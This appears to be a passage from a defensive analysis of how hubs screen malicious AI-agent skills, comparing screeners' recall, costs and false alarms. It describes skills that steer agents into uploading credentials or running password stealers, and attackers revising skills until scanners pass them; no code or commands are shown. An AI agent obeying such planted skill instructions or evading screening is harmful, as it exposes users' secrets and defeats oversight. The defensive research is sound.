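The judge still reads part of every skill because the first stage does not compare skills with each other. In the recall formula, r_f is now the share of malicious skills whose harmful span is among the K spans the system keeps.

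### The laboratory test

The researchers tested the system on 120 benign skills and 21 malicious ones, which they had made by planting attacks in benign skills. Precision was 1.00 in all three configurations:

| Spans sent to the judge | Skills whose harmful span reached the judge | Skills caught | Recall |
|---|---|---|---|
| All | 21 of 21 | 10 | 0.476 |
| Top 5 | 18 of 21 | 11 | 0.524 |
| Top 10 | 20 of 21 | 12 | 0.571 |

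With five spans, the filter limited recall to at most 86%. The judge received the harmful span for 18 skills and caught 11 of them (61%), so it accounted for seven of the ten misses and the filter for three.

The judge likely caught fewer skills when it read every span because of the threshold. If it had a 0.1% chance of wrongly flagging any one span, a benign skill with 73 spans would have a 7% chance of a false alarm, compared with 0.5% for one with five spans. The researchers may therefore have needed a higher threshold to avoid false alarms on the calibration skills when the judge read everything, and the higher threshold would have made it miss some malicious skills. But the three results differ by one skill each, so chance could also explain the differences. The 95% confidence interval for the recall of 0.524 is about 0.32 to 0.72.

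The perfect precision is uncertain too, because a test with 120 benign skills cannot rule out a false-positive rate of about 2.5%.

Attention also did no better than a much simpler filter at K = 5, the setting the researchers went on to use. Ranking spans by the number of suspicious keywords kept the harmful span in 86% of malicious skills, the same as attention. Attention did better only at K = 10, with 95% against 86%, because a keyword filter can't select the harmful spans that contain no keywords.

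### The scan of 134,934 skills

The researchers then scanned skills from Lobehub, ClawHub and skills.sh with K = 5. For comparison, they had the same judge read each skill in full. Two of them reviewed 359 flagged skills:

- 131 were malicious. Of these, 49 were overt, for example because their names announced an attack, and 82 were hidden behind an ordinary purpose.
- 80 were offensive security tools or had both legitimate and harmful uses.
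- 27 were false alarms.
- 121 remained disputed.

One hidden skill offers to prepare a project for deployment. It collects the passwords and keys in the project folder and uploads them to "team shared storage" without asking for confirmation.

The paper reports a precision of 83%, based on 131 malicious skills and 27 false alarms. This calculation excludes more than half of the reviewed flags. Precision would fall to 55% if the offensive tools were counted as errors, and to 36% if the disputed skills were too.

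The 359 flags also appear to come from both methods together, since Locate-and-Judge itself found only 109 of the 131 malicious skills. The paper's figures allow a comparison of the two methods:

| | Locate-and-Judge | Judge reads the whole skill |
|---|---|---|
| Hidden malicious skills found, of 82 | 68 (83%) | 37 (45%) |
| Overt malicious skills found, of 49 | 41 (84%) | 44 (90%) |
| False alarms, of 27 | 23 | 7 |
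| Judge input tokens per skill | 660 | 1,878 |
| Estimated cost of the scan | $34 | $76 |

On these counts, precision is 83% for Locate-and-Judge and 92% for the full reading. Locate-and-Judge finds many more hidden attacks but raises more than three times as many false alarms.

The measured saving is 2.84-fold in tokens per skill, less than the order-of-magnitude cost reduction promised in the paper's abstract. In dollars the saving is 2.2-fold, which cuts the cost of the entire scan by $42, to $34. That $34 covers the judge's tokens but not the cost of running the small model on every skill. The saving would matter more with an expensive judge. With this one, people's time costs far more than either scan. At ten minutes per flag and $40 an hour, checking 359 flags would cost about $2,400.

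The 83% and 45% measure recall only among hidden skills that at least one method found, because nobody reviewed the skills that both passed. The overlap between the methods gives a rough correction. Of the 37 hidden skills that the full reading found, Locate-and-Judge also found 23, or 62%. If the two methods made independent mistakes, 62% would estimate Locate-and-Judge's recall on all hidden skills. The same calculation gives 34% for the full reading. But both use the same judge, so they probably miss many of the same skills, and their true recall is likely even lower.

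The same problem affects the comparison with other screeners. On 65 of the malicious skills, Locate-and-Judge found 62, SkillSpector 13 and Cisco's skill-scanner 10. This sample could not include a skill that only SkillSpector or skill-scanner would have flagged. The sample was also easy, as 58 of the 65 skills were overt. The judge still caught 83% of the skills when it read three randomly chosen spans from each.

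### Why reading less found more

The researchers attribute the difference on hidden skills to dilution, meaning that a short harmful instruction influences the judge's verdict less when pages of harmless text surround it. A 50-token instruction makes up less than 3% of an average skill in the scan, but more than a third of the roughly 132 tokens the judge received for each span. The gap in detection was widest for skills that steal credentials, where Locate-and-Judge found 89% and the full reading found 37%.

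In *LongGuard*, Chen, Wu and Hu (2026) tested this effect on 15 guardrails, which are models that classify text as safe or unsafe. They placed short unsafe texts in harmless Wikipedia passages of increasing length. Average recall fell from 76% at 256 words to 25% at 32,768 words. To test the effect of length alone, they filled the same space with copies of the unsafe text. Recall then fell only from 85% to 68%, so most of the original loss came from the harmless text.

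A second experiment, closer to what Locate-and-Judge does, shows that shortening the input helps only if the filter keeps the right part. Six of the guardrails caught 48% of the unsafe texts when they could read the full text. They caught 70% when Chen and colleagues gave them only the unsafe part, and 24% when given a random part of the same length.

These guardrails look for harmful content such as hate speech, not malicious skills, and many of the test texts were far longer than a typical skill. At about 1,000 words, average recall across the 15 guardrails was only about 12 percentage points lower than at 256 words. Dilution could plausibly explain the gap between 83% and 45%, but the scan did not test this directly. Neither did the laboratory test, because the judge read the spans one at a time in every configuration.

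Judging passages in isolation can also cause false alarms. Ghorbanpour and Fraser (2025), in *Evaluating the Sensitivity of LLMs to Harmful Contents in Long Input*, found that recall fell as they added harmless sentences to a fixed number of harmful ones. But when Llama 3 judged toxic comments one by one, it caught 98% of them with a precision of only 28%. With longer prompts, it estimated the share of harmful text more realistically. Missing context may also explain the extra false alarms from Locate-and-Judge, since a passage about stealing passwords is easier to misread without the page around it. Several of these alarms came from skills that warn users about malware, and others from files of fake passwords used to test password scanners.

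Locate-and-Judge missed 22 malicious skills that the full reading caught. In 13 of them, the attack was a one-line installation command that the parser had not split from the surrounding text, so the filter could not rank it separately. The researchers suggest a second, full reading of the small set of flagged skills, but this would not recover the 22, because they were not flagged. To catch them, the hub would have to read nearly all the skills in full, and the two scans together would cost $110.

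### SkillGate

SkillGate, the screener built by Yang, Fu and colleagues, first searches a skill's text for 530 patterns, such as commands that read stored passwords or decode hidden text and run it. A skill with no match passes without review. For the others, SkillGate extracts up to 20 excerpts around the matches, with 500 characters on either side and a total limit of 8,000 characters. GPT-5.4-mini then judges the skill from these excerpts.

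The researchers tested it on the same 1,650 skills as Cisco's static rules, 150 of them malicious. The results for SkillGate and the full reading are averages over three runs:

| Method | Calls to the judge | Recall | False-positive rate |
|---|---|---|---|
| Patterns alone | 0 | 90.0% | 27.1% |
| SkillGate | 540 | 76.9% | 1.1% |
| Judge reads every skill in full | 1,650 | 80.4% | 1.8% |

SkillGate made about a third as many calls as the full reading and sent 77% fewer tokens. Its filter wrongly discarded 15 of the 150 malicious skills, so no judge could have raised recall above 90%. The judge then missed about 20 of the remaining 135.

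The filter discarded 15 malicious skills, but SkillGate caught only about five fewer than the full reading, which missed about 29. The judge would probably have missed some of the 15 anyway, and the excerpts may have helped it catch others that it would have missed in a full reading. A filter reduces recall by the number of malicious skills it discards that the judge would have caught, minus any that the judge catches only because it reads less.

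A lower threshold can recover some of the lost recall. SkillGate flags a skill when the judge's confidence that it is malicious reaches 0.70. At 0.14, recall would have been 82.4% and the false-positive rate 1.3%, which is better than the full reading at its usual setting. But Yang, Fu and colleagues found this threshold using the test data, which makes it look better than it would on new skills. The number of false alarms also varied between runs, from 7 to 24 among 1,500 benign skills.

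### SkillScreen

A list of patterns gives a hub little control over how many skills go to the judge. In *SkillScreen*, Huang, Quan and colleagues (2026) trained a two-billion-parameter model to use the text of a skill's SKILL.md to score how likely the skill is to be malicious. Because the score is continuous, a hub can set the threshold to reach almost any recall or to send almost any share of skills to the judge. The model scores 1,000 skills in about four and a half minutes on part of one GPU, so it could score the 85,130 skills on ClawHub in under seven hours.

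Large language models are much harder to adjust in this way. Huang and colleagues asked several of them for the probability that each skill was malicious, but each model gave only 13 to 60 distinct values. The first threshold that caught 99% of malicious skills also flagged 87% to 100% of benign ones.

Huang and colleagues trained and tested SkillScreen on the collection that Wang and colleagues assembled. In a test on 447 benign skills and 1,500 malicious skills from attack families that were not in the training data, SkillScreen caught 95.6% of the malicious skills and wrongly flagged 3.3% of the benign ones. At 99% recall, the false-positive rate was 22.6%.

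Moving from the first setting to the second is expensive on a hub where 0.16% of skills are malicious. Among 100,000 skills, the filter would pass on about five more malicious skills and 19,270 more benign ones. Reviewing them with skill-vetter and Qwen3.6 as the judge would cost only $23. But at skill-vetter's false-positive rate of 6.3%, the extra reviews would produce about 1,200 false alarms. Checking those would cost about $8,100, or roughly $1,600 for each additional malicious skill caught. The real cost is probably higher, because the benign skills a filter passes on tend to look more suspicious than average.

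SkillScreen, like Wang and colleagues' word-frequency classifier, raised far more false alarms on the three sources held out of its training. With thresholds meant to give 99% recall, it still caught almost every malicious skill, but it sent 59% of the benign ones for review, compared with 21% in the first test. A hub that had budgeted for 21% would have to pay for almost three times as many reviews. If the hub raised the threshold to keep the share at 21%, recall would fall below 95.6%.

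Much of the problem came from a set of 90 benign skills written from a single template. Their malicious counterparts differed only in their commands, for example deleting files where the benign skill checked free disk space. SkillScreen flagged all 90 benign skills, while GPT-5.5, which Huang and colleagues also tested as a judge, flagged none of them.

### What the filters discard and what the judges miss

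Huang and colleagues also combined the two models, with SkillScreen as the filter and GPT-5.5 as the judge. The next table compares this combination with SkillGate and the laboratory test of Locate-and-Judge. The test sets differ, so the results can't be used to rank the systems.

| System | Benign skills passed on | Malicious skills lost at the filter | Recall with filter | Recall of judge without filter |
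|---|---|---|---|---|
| SkillGate | 27% | 15 of 150 | 76.9% | 80.4% |
| SkillScreen and GPT-5.5, unseen attack families | 21% | about 16 of 1,500 | 71.8% | 72.1% |
| SkillScreen and GPT-5.5, unseen sources | 59% | about 5 of 839 | 42.7% | 42.8% |
| Locate-and-Judge, five spans | parts of all skills | 3 of 21 | 52.4% | 47.6% |

In every row, the judge missed more malicious skills than the filter discarded. In the first of its two tests, SkillScreen sent about 99% of the malicious skills to its judge, GPT-5.5, which missed more than a quarter of them. A filter that discarded nothing would have raised recall by only 0.3 percentage points.

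SkillScreen misses some malicious skills that a judge would recognise. At its default threshold, 42 malicious skills got past all five versions that Huang and colleagues trained, and GPT-5.5 caught nine of these. One is a Chinese-language skill that is advertised as saving tokens but makes the agent refuse every request. Several others contain no clear sign of an attack in SKILL.md, possibly because the harmful part is in a script, which neither model received.

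For this pair, a better prompt for the judge would help far more than a better filter. When Huang and colleagues added eight labelled examples to GPT-5.5's prompt, its recall without a filter rose from 72.1% to 87.9% on the unseen attack families, while its false-positive rate rose from 0.7% to 2.5%. On the unseen sources, recall rose from 42.8% to 60.4%. The examples make each review longer and more expensive, but a hub that sends only a fifth of its skills to the judge bears the extra cost only for those skills.

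## How verdicts hold up when authors adapt

Every recall figure so far comes from a fixed set of skills, whose authors had no chance to see the verdict and try again. But hubs show their verdicts publicly, as Yang and colleagues point out, and anyone can download several of the screeners, so an author whose skill fails can revise it until it passes.

*Runtime Skill Audit* (Lan and Xiao, 2026) tested two rule-based scanners, Aguara and OpenClaw Skill Scanner (a community tool unrelated to Cisco's skill-scanner), against an attacker that adapts. The test started with 20 malicious skills that both scanners caught. The automated attacker revised these skills over several rounds, guided by the scanners' results. OpenClaw Skill Scanner caught none of the 20 after one round, and Aguara caught none after two.

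Lan and Xiao's own system, RSA, still caught 19 or 20 in every round. It runs each skill in an isolated environment, on tasks chosen to trigger whatever looks risky about it. However, the attacker revised the skills to evade the two scanners, not RSA, so the test doesn't show how well RSA would do against an author who had seen its verdicts. In a separate test on 100 skills, RSA had a recall of 88% and a false-positive rate of 8%. *SkillSentry* (2026) also found that some scanners stop detecting a harmful skill once someone rewrites its code, while rewriting has less effect on tests of what the skill does.

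### Ten attempts at a recall of 93%

If a screener has recall r and an author makes n independent attempts, the chance that at least one passes is:

chance = 1 − rⁿ

Skill-vetter with Qwen3.6 had a recall of 93% in Yang and colleagues' test, which gives:

| Attempts | Chance that at least one passes |
|---|---|
| 1 | 7% |
| 3 | 20% |
| 5 | 30% |
| 10 | 52% |
| 20 | 77% |

To keep the chance at 7% over ten attempts, the screener would need a recall of 99.3% on each.

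Real attempts are not independent, so the actual figure can be higher or lower than 52%. The next table shows ten attempts under different assumptions, all with an average recall of 93% on the first attempt.

| Assumption | Chance that at least one of ten passes |
|---|---|
| The verdict on a skill never changes | 7% |
| 90% of malicious skills face a 99% chance of a block each time, the rest a 39% chance | 19% |
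| Attempts are independent | 52% |
| Each revision lowers the chance of a block by five percentage points | 98% |

An author who keeps uploading nearly the same skill fits one of the first two rows. A judge that detects the attack once will probably detect it again, although some verdicts change between runs. An author who learns from each verdict is closer to the last row. Lan and Xiao's result is more extreme than that row, because both scanners started with 100% recall, at which the formula predicts that no attempt would ever succeed. For authors who revise in response to verdicts, 52% is therefore more likely to be too low than too high.

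Attackers return after being caught. On 3 February 2026, ClawHub removed a malicious skill with 7,743 downloads, and a renamed variant was live later that day, according to Snyk's *Inside the 'clawdhub' Malicious Campaign* (2026). OpenSourceMalware's *clawdbot skills ganked your crypto* counted 386 malicious skills published between 31 January and 2 February, all using the same server. Unit 42 found new skills using that server more than three months after researchers first disclosed it. A hub that looks for links such as a shared server can use one detection to find the other skills, which makes repeated attempts less useful to the attacker.

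### When an approved skill changes

A verdict can also fail without any retries. A skill may change after approval, or part of its behaviour may come from outside the reviewed package. Harm may arise only when several skills work together. Text in the package may also influence the judge, because language models can't reliably separate instructions from the material they are assessing. *Dynamic Agent Skills* (2026), a survey, lists scanning skills on admission as just one of eight controls that a safe deployment would need.

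A campaign in the summer of 2026 exploited the gap between review and use. In August, the security company Zenity described it in Zenity Labs' *Attackers Target Agents via The Skill Supply Chain*. An attacker copied the public repository of Paperclip, a popular AI tool, under a very similar name. The main events were:

- **5 July:** skills.sh listed the copied skills, which were still identical to the harmless originals.
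- **11 July:** The attacker changed them so that they led agents to run a program that steals passwords and keys. They were on the hub's trending list that day.
- **1 August:** Zenity Labs noticed the skills, which were trending again.
- **2 August:** The hub and GitHub removed them, within 12 hours of Zenity Labs' report.

By then the hub's counters showed more than 1.7 million installs across the whole family of skills. The number of victims is unknown, because the counters include repeated installs and many users may have installed several of the skills. Copies may remain elsewhere. Users have to remove installed skills themselves, according to TechRadar's *Experts warn malicious AI skills are hitting more victims than ever*.

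The skill files were still harmless on 5 July, so a screener would have been right to pass them, and better recall would not have helped. The altered versions stayed up for 22 days. The same attacker also uploaded two packages to PyPI, the main index of Python software, that were malicious from the start. Researchers spotted one in under two hours and the other within an hour.

### Sealing an approval to exact content

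SIGIL, the registry that Shen and colleagues designed, addresses this gap by tying each approval to the exact content that auditors reviewed:

1. When a publisher submits a skill, the registry calculates a fingerprint from its content, its developer, its previous version and the time.
2. If the auditors approve the skill, the registry stores the approval with that fingerprint, in a record that nobody can alter unnoticed.
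3. When an agent needs the skill, a loader built into the AI provider's service fetches the record, checks the content and permissions, and only then gives the skill to the agent.

Some publishers keep a skill on their own machine and register only a fingerprint of its content. The loader recalculates the fingerprint from the local file each time it loads the skill. Any changed skill needs a new approval.

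Shen and colleagues tested four kinds of database for the registry, with 100 loads each. The average delay per load ranged from 51.7 to 157.6 milliseconds. Querying the registry took up almost all of this time, and the check itself took less than half a millisecond. A user would hardly notice the delay, since a language model often takes seconds to answer.

To test SIGIL's seal, the researchers made five altered versions of each of 50 clean skills. The loader blocked all 250 when they posed as the approved originals. Any change to the content changes the fingerprint, so this result does not depend on a model's judgment. When the researchers instead submitted the altered skills openly as new versions, the audit rejected 95.1% of them and would have approved about 12. At that rate, ten independent attempts would have a 39% chance of getting at least one malicious version approved.

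The seal shows that a skill is unchanged, not that it is safe, so if the auditors approve a malicious skill by mistake, the loader will still deliver it. Like any fingerprint of a package, the seal doesn't cover anything the skill downloads later. The system depends on the loader being the only way to load a skill and on honest auditors holding most of the voting weight. Shen and colleagues acknowledge that an approved skill may turn out to be risky as attacks evolve, but SIGIL has no fixed schedule for auditing it again.

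ClawHub ties its verdicts to specific versions without using such a loader. According to OpenClaw's *HTTP API*, a program can look up the verdict for the exact version a user has installed. However, the moderation status comes from the latest version, so a program that asks about an older version has to check that the two versions match.

### Harm that needs several skills

Reviewing every combination of skills at submission is impractical. The 85,130 skills that Yang and colleagues found on ClawHub form about 3.6 billion pairs. Even at $0.0004 per review, the lowest cost in their test, checking each pair once would cost about $1.4 million. Checking combinations on the user's side makes more sense, because a user with 20 installed skills has only 190 pairs. *SkillProbe* (2026) describes an audit step that checks combinations by simulating how skills might work together in an attack.

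When an agent loads several skills for one request, SIGIL lets it freely use only the permissions that all of them declare and the user has authorised. Anything else needs the user's explicit approval. If one skill declares that it reads files and another that it sends data, they have no permission in common, and the agent has to ask before doing either. Harmless combinations of skills will often trigger the same questions, and users who see many such questions may stop reading them.

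In a test with 33 malicious skills, this rule stopped 90.2% of the attacks. Shen and colleagues mention a single missed case, but a 90.2% success rate on 33 skills would mean about three misses. They claim only that the rule limits permissions. It does not stop skills from working together to mislead the agent through their text or output.

### Reviewing every update

A hub without a sealed registry can still review each new version of a skill before users get it. This costs little for most skills. *Inside the Skill Market* (2026) found that most of the software-engineering skills it studied on ClawHub had never been updated. Only 12 had more than 20 versions, and the most any skill had was 72. At Yang and colleagues' prices, reviewing all 72 versions would cost about 9 cents using skill-vetter with Qwen3.6, or $40 using AI-Infra-Guard with GPT-5.4.

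Each review is also another chance for an error. At skill-vetter's false-positive rate of 6.3%, a harmless skill with ten versions would have a 48% chance of at least one false alarm if the errors were independent. In practice, false alarms would tend to fall repeatedly on the same skills, such as those that handle passwords. An honest publisher loses less if the hub keeps the previous version available during an appeal, as SIGIL does during an audit.

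Update reviews work only if users receive the version the hub reviewed. If a hub links to a repository the author controls, the author can change the skill after the review. The hub can prevent this by storing its own copy or linking to a fixed version of the repository.

### Limiting submissions

If attempts are independent, limiting an author to three would reduce the chance of success from 52% to 20%. But an attacker with four accounts would have 12 attempts and a 58% chance, so the limit's effect depends on how hard it is to open new accounts. A user-written guide on ClawHub says that publishers need a GitHub account at least 14 days old. That requirement slows attackers but doesn't stop those who prepare accounts in advance.

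Rate limits alone do little to stop a patient author. Another user-written page on ClawHub describes a cap of five publications per hour, which would still allow ten attempts in two hours. OpenClaw's documented API limits are much looser, at 3,000 write requests per minute for a logged-in user, and mainly protect the hub's servers.

Limits are more useful against mass uploads. With a cap of five skills a day per account, an attacker would need 26 accounts to publish 386 skills in three days. In two of the collections of malicious skills described earlier, two accounts had published most of the skills.

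A hub could also count blocked submissions instead of all submissions, and send an author's next skill to a human reviewer after three blocks. This wouldn't affect productive honest authors unless the screener kept misjudging their work. ClawHub does something similar with accounts. OpenClaw says it checks publishers for signs of abuse every day and can automatically warn those who reach a set threshold. If they are still over the threshold at the first check after the warning's deadline, the hub may automatically act against the account. The warning protects honest publishers, but it also gives attackers more time.

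### Giving authors less feedback

A detailed report helps an honest publisher fix a false alarm, but it also shows an attacker what the screener noticed. ClawHub shows the public a shortened version of the evidence behind a moderation decision and gives the full version to the skill's owner and the hub's moderators. This does little against a malicious author, who gets the full version as the skill's owner. The hub has also stopped scanning files that users upload only to test them, so authors can no longer use its service to check a skill before publishing it.

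Skill authors can still test skills on their own machines, where submission limits and shorter reports have no effect. pkg.go.dev's *ClawScan* (2026) describes the open-source tool that OpenClaw uses to make its production scanning visible to outsiders. A hub could keep some of its rules or its judge's instructions secret, but that would make mistakes harder for researchers to find, as with the closed screeners on skills.sh.

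An author can tell from even a bare pass or block whether a revision worked. If a hub withholds its reasons, the author learns less from each attempt, and the odds move from the last row of the earlier table towards the independent case. Withholding reasons also harms honest publishers, but the hub could reduce that harm by giving them the full report after a human has looked at the skill.

### Restricting what an approved skill can do

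Runtime restrictions can limit the damage from a malicious skill that passes review, but *Towards Secure Agent Skills* (2026) points out that the skill format doesn't enforce its optional permission fields.

*SkillGuard* (Pan, Sun and colleagues, 2026) adds the missing enforcement by checking every action against a list of permissions that comes with each skill and denying any action that isn't authorised. The user can allow a sensitive action once, allow it for the rest of the session or refuse it. When a skill runs a shell command, a small additional agent works out which permissions the command and its scripts require.

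They tested SkillGuard with three coding agents on Skill-Inject, the collection of attacks planted in legitimate skills:

| Type of attack | Success without SkillGuard | Success with SkillGuard |
|---|---|---|
| Instructions that fit the skill's context | 35.3% | 20.7% |
| Obviously harmful instructions | 36.7% | 18.0% |

SkillGuard usefully reduced the number of successful attacks, but about half or more of those that had worked without it still worked. It increased token use by 24.7% on average, and the three agents completed about as many legitimate tasks as before, with a slight drop for one. The attacks were fixed in advance, so these results, like recall on a fixed test set, don't measure how well SkillGuard works against attackers who adapt.

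Some restrictions barely affect honest skills. *Towards Secure Agent Skills* recommends monitoring the agent's memory and configuration files for unauthorised changes, since no legitimate skill needs to alter the core memory files without the user's knowledge. Access to files and the network is harder to restrict because many skills need both. Wu and colleagues, who built SkillScope to remove unnecessary privileges, say deliberate attacks call for additional controls, such as stronger sandboxes and filters on outgoing traffic.

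Pan and colleagues conclude from their remaining errors that some high-risk permissions need lists of allowed targets, like the named hosts in Metere's proposed manifest.
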